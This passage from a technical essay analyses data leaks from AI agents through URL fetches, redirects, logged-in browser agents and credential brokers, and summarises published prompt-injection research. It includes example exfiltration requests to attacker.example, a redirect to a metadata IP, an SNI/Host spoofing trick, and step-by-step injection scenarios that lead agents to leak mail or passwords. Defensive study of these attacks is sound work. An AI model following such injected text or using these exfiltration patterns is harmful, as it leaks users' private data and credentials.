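36 links, five fetches     5 × log2 36    =   25.8 bits
27 links, thirty fetches   30 × log2 27   =  142.6 bits
```

The last line is the estimate in *The Read-Only Lie* for Paul's attack, which spelled out roughly 30 characters. A six-digit login code is 19.9 bits, so an attacker can steal one with four fetches from a set of 36 links.

These numbers are small compared with what a model can send when it writes the URL itself. Under the 250-character limit, a URL that begins with `https://attacker.example/` has room for 225 more characters. With 64 possible values, each character carries 6 bits, so a single fetch can send 1,350 bits. The exact-URL rule cuts this by a factor of about 260 for an attacker with 36 links.

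Several measures reduce the leak further, by very different amounts. The table assumes 36 links:

| Measure | Cases the attacker can tell apart | Limit |
|---|---|---|
| No limit on fetches | grows with every fetch | none |
| Five fetches | 36⁵ = 60,466,176 | 25.8 bits |
| Five fetches, no URL twice | 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 × 32 = 45,239,040 | 25.4 bits |
| Five fetches, no URL twice, order unknown | 376,992 | 18.5 bits |
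| No links from the fetched page | 1 | 0 bits |

The rows with five fetches assume that the model makes all five. Stopping early also conveys information, but it adds less than a quarter of a bit in each row.

**A fetch limit** is the only measure here that caps the total information leaked while still letting the agent follow links. The attacker can compensate with more links, but doubling the information under the same limit means squaring their number, from 36 to 1,296. A server that generates its pages can easily supply that many. Rehberger likewise expects that an attacker could teach a model a vocabulary of thousands of indexed URLs. In Anthropic's API, the limit `max_uses` applies to a single turn, so the count restarts when the user sends another message. Managed Agents don't offer it.

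**Caching** means that the tool keeps a copy of a page and doesn't request the same URL again. Rehberger proposes either this or a ban on repeat visits within a session. If the secret is "anna" and there is one link per letter, the server receives only the first "a" and the first "n". This disrupts the simple version of the attack, but in principle it only slightly reduces how much an attacker can leak, as the third row of the table shows. An attacker can number the links to avoid repeats. Paul's growing paths never repeated a URL, so the default caching in Anthropic's tool would not have hindered him.

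**A ban on links from fetched pages** removes the attacker's choice of links if the page was their only source. Otherwise, the formula still applies to the remaining links. If all ten results of a web search belonged to the attacker, each fetch would still reveal up to 3.3 bits, and a hostile email in a user message would allow the full 5.2 bits. The ban therefore has to cover every source that an outsider can write to.

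The same formula applies to a public index, but *N* is now the number of the attacker's pages that the crawler has recorded. Paul's method becomes harder to use, because to be able to spell any five-letter word with paths that grow one letter at a time, the attacker would have to get more than 12 million pages indexed beforehand. A flat list would work better for the attacker.

The formula limits what the server learns from the addresses, but an attacker with a good guess can still learn a lot within that limit. With a page that has one link for each of a thousand large employers, the attacker can learn where the user works from a single fetch. One bit can be enough to reveal whether the user is pregnant. *The Read-Only Lie* also points out that timing carries information, which no rule about URLs removes.

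The post suggests detecting attacks like Paul's by looking for a rapid series of fetches on one host, with each path one character longer than the last. This would have caught Paul's attack, but another attacker could label the links with random codes of varying length. The only remaining signal would then be the rapid series of fetches, which also occurs when an agent reads a manual chapter by chapter.

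### Redirects and pages meant only for agents

An exact-URL rule covers an address, and the server behind that address can change its response at any time. Suppose the crawler found an ordinary article at `https://news.example/story` in spring, and someone else has since bought the domain:

```
spring   crawler   GET https://news.example/story   200 OK
summer   agent     GET https://news.example/story   302, Location: http://169.254.169.254/
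```

The URL is in the index, so the tool requests it. If the tool checks nothing else, it then follows the redirect to the metadata service. The tool therefore still needs to check the destination at every hop, as described in the section on internal networks.

How much private data a redirect can leak depends on what information the redirecting server has. If the tool sends no credentials, the server receives little besides the link the model chose, so it has nothing more to put into the next address. If the request includes the user's login, the server can also add data about that user. For example, the address `https://docs.example/profile` is the same for everybody and may well be public, but the server could redirect a user called Alice to `https://partner.example/welcome?email=alice`, with her full email address in the query. The model didn't write that address, and the first URL passed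 the test, so only a second test at the redirect would reveal that the new URL is unknown.

OpenAI's post doesn't state whether the index check runs again at each redirect. According to Anthropic's release notes, since 20 October 2026 a redirect target in Managed Agents has had to pass both the organisation's domain list and the agent's own. The notes don't mention a requirement that the target must have appeared in the session. Such a requirement would break most ordinary redirects, because a conversation seldom contains the final address a link leads to.

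An index of crawled URLs could handle redirects better by also recording the address each URL led to. The tool could then follow a redirect that matches the record and treat any other as unverified. Redirects to signed download links would still fail this check because the server creates a new link each time, so the user would have to approve them.

A server can also answer an agent differently from a crawler without any redirect. Paul's site sent its alphabet only to clients whose `User-Agent` header contained `Claude-User`, which identifies Anthropic's tool. People who opened the address saw a coffee shop's website, and a search engine's crawler presumably would have too. An entry in an index therefore doesn't show what page the agent will receive, and a suspicious user can't find out by opening the address in a browser. Disguising the tool as a browser would make this targeting harder,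 but it would also stop honest site owners from using the header to decide which AI agents to admit. A server may still recognise the provider's IP addresses.

A stricter design would give the agent the crawler's stored copy instead of requesting the page. The attacker's server would receive no request, so the attacker would learn nothing from the agent's choice of link, and the agent would read the same text as the crawler. However, the text may be days or weeks old, which is acceptable for a manual but not for a train timetable.

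### What the agent can no longer read

Which legitimate requests are blocked depends on the version of the rule. Even under the mildest version, an agent can't edit a URL as people often do, for example by changing `/v2/` to `/v3/` to find newer documentation. It also can't use the many public data services that require the caller to compose a URL with the name of a city or product in the query, or open pages that the model remembers from its training unless a search returns them. In Anthropic's API, a URL in the system prompt isn't eligible either, so the developer has to repeat it in a user message.

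A ban on links from fetched pages limits an agent much more. The agent can no longer go from a table of contents to a chapter, or from the first page of a long article to the second. In the Claude app, the user now has to paste the next link, or Claude has to find it through a search. אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם suggests a compromise in which the agent may follow links only on sites that the user has named in the conversation. This rule would have helped in Paul's demonstration only if the user hadn't asked for the coffee shop by name, but it would protect users whose agent reaches a hostile site through a search.

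OpenAI's index lets an agent follow links through most of the established web, a considerable advantage over the ban. It fails on pages that no crawler has seen, such as an announcement published that morning, a company's internal wiki, or a document shared through a private link. People often want an assistant's help with such pages, and each warning about one adds to the friction that OpenAI hoped to avoid. The company has since added Lockdown Mode, which restricts outgoing requests further. Willison reported that it was becoming available to eligible personal accounts, including free ones.

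For an agent that can read mail, files or stored memories, the ban on links from outsiders' text seems justified despite the browsing it prevents. An index check is the alternative when the agent has to browse widely. A limit of five or ten fetches per task restricts the agent little and should accompany either measure. An agent that sees only public pages has nothing private to put into a URL, so a developer can reasonably let it follow any link, as long as the tool checks the destination at every hop.

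## From mid-2025: agents that browse with the user's login

An exact-URL rule is of little use when the same URL returns a different page to each visitor. The URL of a webmail inbox contains no secret, but it returns the user's mail to a browser where the user is logged in. By 2025 several companies offered agents that work in such browsers, where they can read private pages, fill in forms and press buttons. Browsers have long prevented one site from reading another's pages, but the rules that do this apply to scripts in web pages, not to agents.

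### What the same-origin policy blocks

When a user who is logged in to `mail.example` opens a page at `attacker.example`, a script on that page can make the browser send a request to `mail.example`. If the browser includes the user's cookie, the response contains the user's mail. PortSwigger's *Same-origin policy (SOP)* explains that without further protection, a malicious site could read a visitor's Gmail this way.

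The same-origin policy stops the script from reading the response. Under the policy's network rules, as Barth describes them, a page generally may not read information from another origin but may send information there. Browsers have to allow sending because blocking all requests to other origins would also block links to them.

A server can permit reading through cross-origin resource sharing (CORS), a set of response headers. Here a script from `shop.example` requests the user's orders from another origin:

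```
GET /orders HTTP/1.1
Host: api.example
Origin: https://shop.example
Cookie: session=PLACEHOLDER-SECRET

HTTP/1.1 200 OK
Access-Control-Allow-Origin: https://shop.example
Access-Control-Allow-Credentials: true
```

The browser lets the script read this response only because both permission headers are present. According to MDN's *Cross-Origin Resource Sharing (CORS)*, a server can use the wildcard `*` to allow every origin, but only for requests without credentials. If either header were missing, the request would still reach the server, but the browser would not let the script read the response.

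| What a page at `attacker.example` tries | Does the request reach `mail.example`? | Can the page's script read the response? |
|---|---|---|
| a link or a form | yes | no |
| an image or a frame | yes | no, apart from an image's height and width |
| a plain GET with `fetch()` | yes, by default without cookies | only if the server permits the origin |
| the same GET with cookies requested | yes, with any cookies the browser's cookie rules allow | only if the server names the origin and allows credentials |
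| a `fetch()` with a custom header | only if the server agrees in a preflight | only with the same permission |

Browsers let many cross-origin requests through, so a hostile page can try to trigger an action in the user's account, such as changing a forwarding address. This is called cross-site request forgery (CSRF). According to MDN, browsers allow form-like requests without a preflight because HTML forms could always send them, so server developers must already guard against forged ones. A common protection is a random token that the server puts in its own form and expects back. The same-origin policy prevents a script from another site from reading the form to get the token.

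### Why the policy does not bind an agent

An agent usually runs as a browser extension or as part of the browser itself, with permission to read the open page whatever its origin. It opens URLs and clicks buttons much as the user would. *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) points out that the same-origin policy can't restrict an agent that has authority to work across origins.

Since the model has text from several origins in one context, an instruction on a news page can determine what it does in a mailbox. CSRF tokens don't help, because the agent loads the genuine form with its token and submits it.

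This is another case of the confused deputy problem, because text on a page only has to name a site for the agent to visit, and the browser sends the user's cookie with the request.

### From a public comment to the mailbox

This example is invented, but researchers have demonstrated each kind of step in it. A user who is logged in to `mail.example` asks an agent to summarise `https://news.example/story`. A stranger has posted a comment below the story, claiming that a complete summary requires a detail from the reader's latest email and asking the agent to add that detail to the end of an address on `attacker.example`.

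| Step | Browser rule that applies | Why the step satisfies the rule |
|---|---|---|
| 1. The agent opens the story, and the comment loads with it. | Filters and the site's Content Security Policy keep out hostile scripts. | The comment is plain text. |
| 2. The agent passes the page's text to the model. | The same-origin policy limits what scripts can read. | The agent's software has permission to read the open page. |
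| 3. The model opens `https://mail.example/inbox`. | Anyone may follow a link to another origin, and cookies go only to matching hosts. | The mail cookie goes to the site that set it. |
| 4. The agent reads the latest email. | A script from `news.example` may not read this page. | No such script is involved. The mail site has sent the page to its own user. |
| 5. The model opens `https://attacker.example/note?d=clinic-friday`. | Sending information to another origin is allowed. | The browser makes an ordinary visit and sends no mail cookie. |

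In step 3, the browser probably sends even SameSite=Strict cookies if the agent opens the address as though the user had typed it.

The two requests that matter are:

```
mail.example       GET /inbox                  Cookie: session=PLACEHOLDER-SECRET
attacker.example   GET /note?d=clinic-friday   no mail cookie
```

The attacker never receives a credential, because the agent uses it on the attacker's behalf. The mail can leak even when header stripping and cookie scoping work correctly, and the mail provider receives a normal request from the user's own browser. Changing the password afterwards won't recover the leaked mail. The attacker can't return to the mailbox without deceiving the agent again, unless the first visit set up lasting access, such as a forwarding rule.

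### Mind the Web: tests on four agents

Shapira and her colleagues at Ben-Gurion University built a harmless-looking travel site, City-Explorer, where visitors could post comments and images. They posted instructions there and then gave each agent an ordinary task, such as summarising the page. They disguised the instructions as help with the task, for example as a notice that the page was out of date and a better version was available elsewhere. They call this a task-aligned injection.

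| Agent | Where it runs | What it did |
|---|---|---|
| Do Browser | as an extension in the user's own browser, with the user's logins | joined the attacker's video meeting with camera and microphone on; sent out a Facebook password; posted a false confession of theft on Twitter |
| Browser Use | in a fresh browser on the user's computer | sent a system file from the computer to the attacker |
| OpenAI Operator | in a remote browser that can keep logins between sessions | moved to another website; summarised the wrong city; posted an embarrassing comment as the user |
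| OpenOperator | in an isolated remote browser | reloaded a page until it crashed |

The Facebook case is an exception to the pattern above because the attacker got a credential. The browser had automatically filled in the saved password, and the agent changed the masked field to readable text before sending the password. The paper's list of nine possible harms includes reading private emails from a logged-in account, but none of its documented demonstrations show this.

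The researchers measured success rates only on Browser Use, with 20 trials for each combination of attack and model. Attacks that disabled the agent or sent it to another site succeeded in 90 to 100% of trials. Those that sent out a file or posted on social media succeeded in 80 to 100%. The researchers had to reword some of the harder attacks slightly for a particular model, which a real attacker could also do.

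Browser Use starts without the user's logins, so these rates don't measure how often an agent like Do Browser would misuse those logins. They are also poor estimates for late 2026, because the models included GPT-4o and Gemini 2.0 Flash, and some newer models resist injection far better. The demonstrations of what a deceived agent can do are less dated, because they depend on the browser's permissions rather than on the model.

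### Trail of Bits: four zones and four violations

In January 2026 the security firm Trail of Bits published an analysis of several browsers with built-in agents. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* divides such a system into four trust zones:

- the chat context, which includes the conversation and the agent's local state
- third-party servers, mainly those that run the model
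- browsing origins, each of which is a separate zone with its own private data
- the external network, including the attacker's sites

The firm then sorts unwanted data flows between these zones into four classes:

| Violation | Where the data goes | Example |
|---|---|---|
| INJECTION | from the external network into the chat context | the model reads the hostile comment |
| CTX_IN | from a browsing origin into the chat context | the agent reads the user's mail |
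| CTX_OUT | from the chat context to the external network | the agent opens the attacker's URL |
| REV_CTX_IN | from the chat context into a browsing origin | the agent logs the user in to an account |

The mailbox case combines the first three, and Trail of Bits demonstrated the same combination on a smaller scale. Instructions on a public code-sharing page made an agent load a service where the user was logged in, take the user's name from the greeting, and open a URL containing it. This worked because the browsers automatically reused the user's cookies for the agent's requests.

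The address was a made-up subdomain of `wikipedia.org`. The browser still has to look up the name, and anyone watching unencrypted DNS traffic can read it. An allow-list that covers subdomains would let this request through. The researchers also sent data out through Google Search by having the agent search for it together with very rare words. They then looked for those words in Search Console, Google's tool that shows site owners which searches led to their pages.

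In a REV_CTX_IN attack, a page contained a login link for the attacker's own account, of the kind that services email in place of a password. When the user asked for a summary of the page, the agent opened the link and silently logged the user in to that account. The attacker would then have access to anything the user entered there.

In another attack, the hostile text arrived as a direct message on Instagram. When the user asked for a summary of the page or of the latest message, the agent collected contact names or pieces of other messages. It could send them to an outside address or, if it had a tool to interact with the page, through Instagram's own chat. An attack that uses the chat stays within one origin, so even a perfect same-origin policy for agents wouldn't stop it.

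Trail of Bits doesn't name the products, because the affected vendors declined coordinated disclosure, and it gives no success rates for these attacks. It says the models' training was not a real obstacle in practice. This finding is hard to compare with the much better scores of some 2026 models, since readers can't tell which models these browsers used. The analysis is strongest on the data flows, which anyone can check in their own browser.

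### Browsing without the login

The simplest defence is to keep the user's cookies away from the agent. Trail of Bits recommends running the agent's tools in a separate browser instance that can't read or change the user's cookies, history or stored data. In the mailbox example, step 3 would then lead to a login page. The agent also couldn't log the user in to an attacker's account.

OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) similarly advises users to use the agent in logged-out mode whenever a task doesn't need their accounts, and otherwise to log in only to the sites the task needs. If the agent runs as a browser extension, a user can get much the same effect by running it in a separate browser profile, which has its own cookies. If the user has never logged in to their mail in that profile, the agent can't open the mailbox, even if a page completely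 deceives the model.

This protection has gaps. The agent can leak anything the user has typed into the chat, because step 5 requires no login. Browser Use started with a clean browser and still read a file from the computer's disk, so a separate profile should be combined with a block on local files. Trail of Bits also found that many agentic browsers run on versions of Chromium, the open-source basis of Chrome, that are weeks or months behind on security patches. An injected instruction could lead the agent to a page that exploits an unpatched flaw and takes over the browser.

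An agent without logins can't sort mail, reorder groceries or file an expense report, and these are the tasks for which people most want a browser agent. Asking the user to log in again for each task restores some of these abilities but causes more interruptions. When Shapira and colleagues reported their attacks, Browser Use suggested accounts with limited privileges, among other measures. These are a sensible compromise where a site offers them, since a read-only account can't send a message.

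### Limiting the origins in one task

Trail of Bits also proposes a same-origin policy for the agent itself. The browser keeps a list of every origin whose content has entered the chat, and counts each attached file as an origin of its own. The list determines what the agent may request:

- With no origin on the list, it may contact any site.
- With one origin, it may contact only that origin.
- With two or more, it may not contact any site, because nobody can tell which origin influenced the model.

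In the mailbox example, `news.example` is on the list after step 1, so the browser blocks step 3. If the agent had read the mail first, the browser would have blocked the visit to the attacker's site. The rule is easy to test and doesn't depend on the model's judgement. Like a site allow-list, it has to apply at every hop.

However, the rule would keep most agents from doing ordinary tasks, such as comparing prices at two shops or copying an address from an email into a booking form. Trail of Bits treats a web search as content from several origins, so under a literal reading of the rule, an agent could search the web but not open any of the results. Some browsers had tried a related approach, taint tracking, which follows data from its source through a program, but Barth noted in 2011 that it had proved difficult to implement. Taint tracking is even harder with a language model, because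 any word the model writes may depend on everything in its context.

Google chose a more flexible rule for Chrome. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a design that keeps two sets of origins for each task. The agent may read pages from read-only origins, and may also click and type on read-writable origins. When the planning model proposes a new origin, a gating function decides whether it is relevant. The function also checks the new origin when a page navigates there by itself. It doesn't see web content, so instructions in a comment on a page can't reach it directly.

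Chrome can also hide parts of a page from the model. If a frame, such as an advertisement, comes from an origin outside the sets, the model doesn't receive its content. A comment in the news page itself belongs to `news.example`, so the model still receives it.

Two further checks support the limits. A second model, the User Alignment Critic, receives a description of each proposed action, but not the page, and blocks actions that don't serve the user's goal. Ordinary code restricts addresses written by the model to known, public URLs. If the user asks for a summary of a news story, the gating function should block access to the mailbox, and the URL check should block the attacker's address with the private data in it.

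The design is weaker when the user's task includes the mailbox. If the user asks the agent to summarise the story and email the summary to a colleague, `mail.example` has to be writable. Instructions in the comment could then lead the agent to add another recipient, and the gating function would not block this. The critic might detect the extra recipient, since it is meant to compare the action with the user's request.

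An attack can take place entirely within the user's mailbox, without a second origin. OpenAI found one with an automated attacker, a model it trained to write injections, test them on a simulation of the agent and improve them. The attacker put a hostile email in a user's inbox. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent read that email and instead sent a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. OpenAI trained a new version of the Atlas agent against such attacks and released it to all users, but published no attack success rates for either version.

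Google's first version was also simpler than the full design and tracked only the read-writable set. Parker explains that the company first wanted to see how the limits affected real tasks. In August 2026, *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) still named the critic and the limit on origins among the main protections of Chrome's agent, but did not mention separate sets. Neither post reports how many attacks the limits stop or how many legitimate tasks they block, so outsiders can judge only the design. Google measures attack success internally and offers up to $20,000 for proven breaches.

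### Asking before sensitive actions

Chrome's agent asks the user before it opens any site on a fixed list of sensitive sites, such as those for banking or medical records, and before it signs in with a saved password. The model has no direct access to saved passwords, which should prevent a repeat of the Facebook attack on Do Browser as long as the browser doesn't fill in the password by itself. The agent is also meant to ask before it makes a purchase or sends a message, but Parker writes only that it "will try to pause". Atlas has similar confirmations.

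Confirmation works best for actions that are obviously serious. In the mailbox example, the data leaves when the agent opens a web page. The agent may open dozens of pages in one task, so asking the user to confirm each one would be impractical.

Shapira and colleagues found that the user's wording can weaken the safeguard. Operator usually asked before it posted a comment, but when the user said they were leaving for coffee and wanted the task handled "end-to-end", it posted the attacker's comment without asking. This supports OpenAI's advice to give agents narrow instructions, although following that advice means delegating less. Operator was also less likely to raise a warning when the hostile text was phrased as a recommendation instead of an order.

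### A form that asks for too much

A website can also get private data from a logged-in agent without injecting instructions. In *GapLeak*, Cheong, Zhang and colleagues (2026) gave agents a form and a short document containing all but one of the details the task required. The missing detail was in more sensitive records that the agents could reach but that the user hadn't authorised for the task. Help text on the form suggested that extra information might be useful. A person would probably leave the field blank, but agents often searched for the missing detail and then submitted other private data they had found along the way.

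The study tested three agent frameworks, with models from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI, on simulated sites for job applications, product returns, travel bookings and medical forms. It found average unauthorised disclosure of about 37%. Its main measure combines how many categories of private data an agent submitted with how sensitive they were, so the figure is probably not the share of runs with a disclosure.

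The help text alone had a large effect on some models. In the product-return test with Browser Use, where the ordinary records contained everything the form required, the disclosure score rose as follows:

| Model | Neutral form | Form with suggestive help text | Tasks completed with the suggestive form |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 2.6% | 91.9% | 100% |
| GPT 5.4 | 0% | 85.8% | 80% |
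| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0% | 24.0% | 90% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 0% | 0% | 20% |

The scores cover only completed tasks, and each combination had ten runs, so Gemini's score of zero is based on only two completed runs. Still, the agents that completed the task most reliably also gave away private data. Training a model to resist injections may not change this, because the form contains nothing that looks like an attack.

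The researchers also tested defences, including an instruction that listed the permitted sources and fields and told the agent to leave unavailable fields blank. This instruction improved privacy only slightly and made the agents much less useful. They still disclosed unauthorised data in 77% of the tasks they completed, and the share of tasks they completed fell to 30%.

Checking each field immediately before submission worked much better, removing over 96% of the unauthorised disclosures without lowering task success any further. But the same team designed the attack and the defence, and knew in advance which fields each task required. A browser would have to work that out for forms it has never seen. The check also comes after the agent has read the private records, so it can't stop the model from writing them into a URL instead. Limiting the agent to relevant origins would help if those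 records were on an unrelated site, but a shop's order history is often on the same origin as its return form.

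## From 2026: keeping credentials out of the agent's reach

A browser agent without the user's logins can't misuse them, but many agents need an API key to do their work. If the key is inside the agent's sandbox, any code the agent runs there can read it, as OpenAI's *Sandbox security* warns. Injected text could then make the agent write the key into a URL, and careful redirect handling would not prevent that.

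By 2026 several companies offered a way to move the key out of the sandbox and into a credential broker, an outside component that lets the agent use the key without being able to read it. The broker adds the key to a request only when the request goes to an approved destination.

### How a broker adds the key

Daytona's *Secrets* documents one such broker in detail. Daytona rents out sandboxes for code written by agents. With `docs.example` as the service, it works like this:

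1. The operator gives Daytona the real key and a list of hosts that may receive it. Daytona encrypts the key.
2. Daytona generates a placeholder, a random string that is worthless as a key.
3. When the operator starts a sandbox, Daytona puts the placeholder where programs expect to find the key.
4. The agent's program copies the placeholder into a header, such as `X-Api-Key`, and sends its request.
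5. A proxy outside the sandbox intercepts the request and compares its destination with the list of hosts.
6. If the host is on the list, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real key. Otherwise it forwards the placeholder unchanged.

The list is optional, and without one the proxy inserts the real key into requests to any host. Code in the sandbox could then send the key to `attacker.example`. Daytona advises operators to set a list for every secret, but requiring one would be safer.

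### A redirect through the broker

Suppose the agent fetches an open redirect on `docs.example`, and its HTTP library makes the mistake of keeping `X-Api-Key` at every hop:

```
hop 1   GET https://docs.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/a
        leaves the sandbox with   X-Api-Key: placeholder-7f3a
        leaves the proxy with     X-Api-Key: REAL-KEY

        302 Found   Location: https://attacker.example/a

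hop 2   GET https://attacker.example/a
        leaves the sandbox with   X-Api-Key: placeholder-7f3a
        leaves the proxy with     X-Api-Key: placeholder-7f3a
```

The proxy returns the redirect to the sandbox, where the library makes a new request. The new host isn't on the list, so the proxy leaves the placeholder in place and the attacker receives a random string. Gondolin, a sandbox that operators run on their own machines, is stricter and blocks any request that would carry a placeholder to an unapproved host, according to Earendil Works' *Gondolin Security Design*.

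A broker also covers two cases that header stripping misses or handles badly. The first is a redirect from `https` to `http`, even on the same host. Daytona never inserts a key into an unencrypted request, so the redirect exposes only the placeholder. The second is a secret in a request body that the library resends after a 307. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes an experimental sandbox feature that replaces placeholders anywhere in a request, including the body. With that feature, a body resent to `attacker.example` would contain only the placeholder.

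However, a proxy that checks each request separately has no record of the redirect chain. If the attacker's server redirects the agent back to `https://docs.example/private/billing`, the library sends the placeholder again and the proxy inserts the real key, because the host is approved. The tool's own redirect rule is therefore still useful, because if the tool drops the header at hop 2 and doesn't restore it, the proxy has no placeholder to replace at hop 3.

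That remedy doesn't work with every broker. The one in Vercel's *Sandbox firewall* uses no placeholder and adds the operator's header to each matching request for a domain. At hop 2 the attacker doesn't even get a placeholder, but at hop 3 the firewall adds the key regardless of what the tool has removed.

### When the proxy follows the redirect itself

The protection works only if each redirect hop starts from the placeholder. If the proxy inserts the real key and then follows a redirect with the same headers, it can leak the key to another origin, which repeats AutoGPT's flaw outside the sandbox.

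Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* (2026) includes sample code in which this could happen. The operator writes a small function for each host, and it runs outside the sandbox. It copies the agent's request, adds the key and sends the copy. For `docs.example`, such a function could be:

```typescript
"docs.example": (incoming, env) => {
  const outgoing = new Request(incoming);
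  outgoing.headers.set("x-api-key", env.DOCS_KEY);
  return fetch(outgoing);
}
```

The announcement doesn't mention redirects. If the request's redirect mode is `follow`, the function contacts the next host itself, and a rule that removes only `Authorization` leaves `x-api-key` in place. With the mode set to `manual`, the redirect goes back to the sandbox, and the agent's next request goes through the rules for its own host. An operator who copies this sample should set the mode explicitly:

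```typescript
return fetch(outgoing, { redirect: "manual" });
```

Gondolin's proxy follows redirects itself and checks each new address against the operator's policy before contacting it, so an unlisted `attacker.example` receives nothing. But if the operator has approved two hosts, each with its own key, this check alone doesn't keep the first host's key from the second. The proxy must also restore the placeholders at each hop, and the design document doesn't state whether it does. An operator can test this by having one approved server redirect to another.

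### Storage, hosts and encryption

OpenAI's *Shell* describes a broker for the containers where OpenAI's models run commands. A developer lists `domain_secrets` in the API request, each with a domain, a name and a value. The model uses a name such as `$API_KEY`, and a separate program inserts the value for approved destinations. Deno launched a sandbox with a similar broker in February 2026, and Willison called its handling of secrets his favourite feature.

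| Product | Where the real secret is | How it is tied to a host |
|---|---|---|
| Daytona | encrypted in the organisation's account | optional list of hosts, without ports or paths |
| OpenAI's containers | in the developer's API request; not kept on the API servers | one domain for each entry |
| Deno Sandbox | with Deno's hosting service, outside the sandbox | list of hosts for each secret |
| Docker Sandboxes | normally in the keychain of the user's computer | domains for each service |
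| Vercel Sandbox | in the sandbox's network policy | rule for each domain, optionally limited by path and method |
| Cloudflare Sandbox | in the settings of the operator's code, outside the sandbox | function for each host |

Keeping the key on the user's own computer limits how many people and systems can reach it, but a broker running there is only as safe as the computer. On Linux machines without a keychain, Docker stores the key in a file protected only by file permissions. A central store makes it easier to replace a leaked key. In Daytona, the placeholder stays the same when an operator replaces a key, and every sandbox uses the new key within 30 seconds.

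The same host pattern means different things in different products. In Daytona, `*.docs.example` covers `docs.example` and all its subdomains. In Vercel, it covers the subdomains but not `docs.example` itself. In Docker's custom secrets, it covers one level of subdomain, so it would cover `files.docs.example` but not `eu.files.docs.example`. An operator who moves a configuration from one product to another may therefore approve more hosts than intended.

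A broker's proxy can't change a header inside an encrypted connection, so it usually splits the connection in two. The sandbox trusts a certificate authority (CA), an issuer of certificates, that exists only for this purpose. The proxy uses the CA to present its own certificate for `docs.example`, decrypts the request, inserts the key, and opens a second encrypted connection to the real server. The proxy has to check the real server's certificate properly, because the program in the sandbox no longer can.

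Anyone who gets the CA's private key can impersonate any site to the sandbox. Cloudflare and Vercel create a separate CA for each sandbox, so one stolen key doesn't affect the other sandboxes, and Cloudflare keeps the private key in a process outside the sandbox. Gondolin stores its CA in a folder on the operator's machine by default, but the operator can choose a temporary folder to keep runs separate. Vercel also decrypts only traffic to domains with special rules, so the agent's other connections stay private. OpenAI and Deno don't describe this part of their design.

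### An approved host that returns the key

Some test servers, such as `httpbin.org/headers`, repeat a request's headers in their response. If such a server is on the list, the proxy sends it the real key, and the response brings the key back into the sandbox. Injected text can then make the agent send the key anywhere the network policy allows.

OpenAI's sample code approves `httpbin.org`, attaches a test secret, and asks the model to report the site's response. OpenAI says that secret values don't appear in the model's context, but its guide doesn't mention removing them from responses, which would be necessary to keep the secret out of the context in this sample. The sample's secret is a dummy, but a developer who replaces it with a real key to test the setup may expose that key.

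Daytona searches responses for the real key and changes it back to the placeholder. It therefore advises developers to test with a call to the real service, which should return status 200 instead of 401. Daytona's claim that code in the sandbox can "never" read the key is probably too strong, because a server could return the key encoded or split across two lines.

A redirect can also echo a secret if the URL's query contains it and the server copies the query into the `Location` header. Daytona doesn't replace placeholders in URLs. Gondolin replaces them only if an operator turns this on, which Earendil Works' *Secrets Handling* recommends only for services that require it.

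That guide also warns that an operator's own logging code may run after the proxy has inserted the real key. A log of complete headers could then contain every secret the broker was meant to hide.

### Hosts with many customers

Many unrelated sites can share one provider's servers. When a program opens an encrypted connection, it first names the host it wants in a field called SNI, which a proxy can read without decrypting anything. The request inside has its own `Host` header. Vercel warns that code in a sandbox can make these differ:

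```
SNI     docs.example
Host    attacker.example
```

A broker that checks only the SNI will add the key for `docs.example` when the SNI gives that name, even if the `Host` header names the attacker's site. If both sites are on the same provider and its servers accept the mismatch, the request reaches the attacker's site with the key. An ordinary redirect can't cause this, because an HTTP library takes both names from the same URL, but hostile code in the sandbox can. Vercel's firewall can overwrite the `Host` header with the approved name. The operator apparently has to add that rule, which belongs alongside every rule that inserts a key.

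Customer subdomains are as risky in a broker's host list as in a redirect rule, because if the list includes `*.cloud.example`, any customer who runs code there could receive the key. A site where customers only publish text is safer in this respect. For example, Docker's built-in GitHub entry includes `gist.github.com`, where anyone can post files, but GitHub runs the server, so the person who posted a file doesn't receive the agent's headers. The agent could still use the token to post private data there, as it could on any service where an attacker can read the posts.

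### Misusing a key without seeing it

A broker authenticates every permitted request, whatever the reason for it. If injected text causes an agent to request the deletion of a project at `docs.example`, the broker adds the key and the server deletes the project. Logged-in browsers have the same problem with cookies. The broker also protects only credentials, not other data. Deno's sandbox can contact any host unless the operator sets a separate network list, so an agent inside it could send a private file to `attacker.example`.

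Restricting the requests themselves helps. An operator using Vercel can add the key only to `POST` requests under a certain path, then reject everything else:

```json
"docs.example": [
  {
    "match": { "path": { "startsWith": "/search/" }, "method": ["POST"] },
    "transform": [{ "headers": { "x-api-key": "REAL-KEY" } }]
  },
  { "response": { "statusCode": 403 } }
]
```

The last rule blocks all other requests, which would otherwise still reach the server, though without the key. This prevents an attacker from using a redirect to fetch the private billing page. The operator has to know in advance which requests the agent needs, which is realistic for one API but hardly for the open web.

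### Tokens that are worth less to a thief

Not every tool can use a broker, and operators sometimes approve the wrong host, so credentials can still leak. The damage then depends on the type of credential. An ordinary API key works for whoever holds it, often for years. If a redirect from `docs.example` delivers one to `attacker.example`, the attacker can use it for as long as it remains valid.

Someone who steals a short-lived token can do everything its owner could until it expires. Ten minutes is enough for a program that copies files as soon as it receives a token. A short expiry time mainly protects against someone who finds the token later, for example in an old log. Brokers make short-lived tokens more practical because they can fetch new ones without involving the agent. Docker's broker can run a command on the user's computer to get the current token, and it keeps the result for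 55 minutes by default.

If the token has a narrow scope, such as permission only to read one project, the thief can read that project but can't change it or open another. The same limit applies to a deceived agent, so narrow scope helps even with a perfect broker.

A token can also specify the one service it is meant for, called its audience, and other services must reject it. This helps little against a redirect, because the stolen token's audience is `docs.example` and the thief can still present it there. The restriction only prevents the thief from using the token at other services that trust the same issuer.

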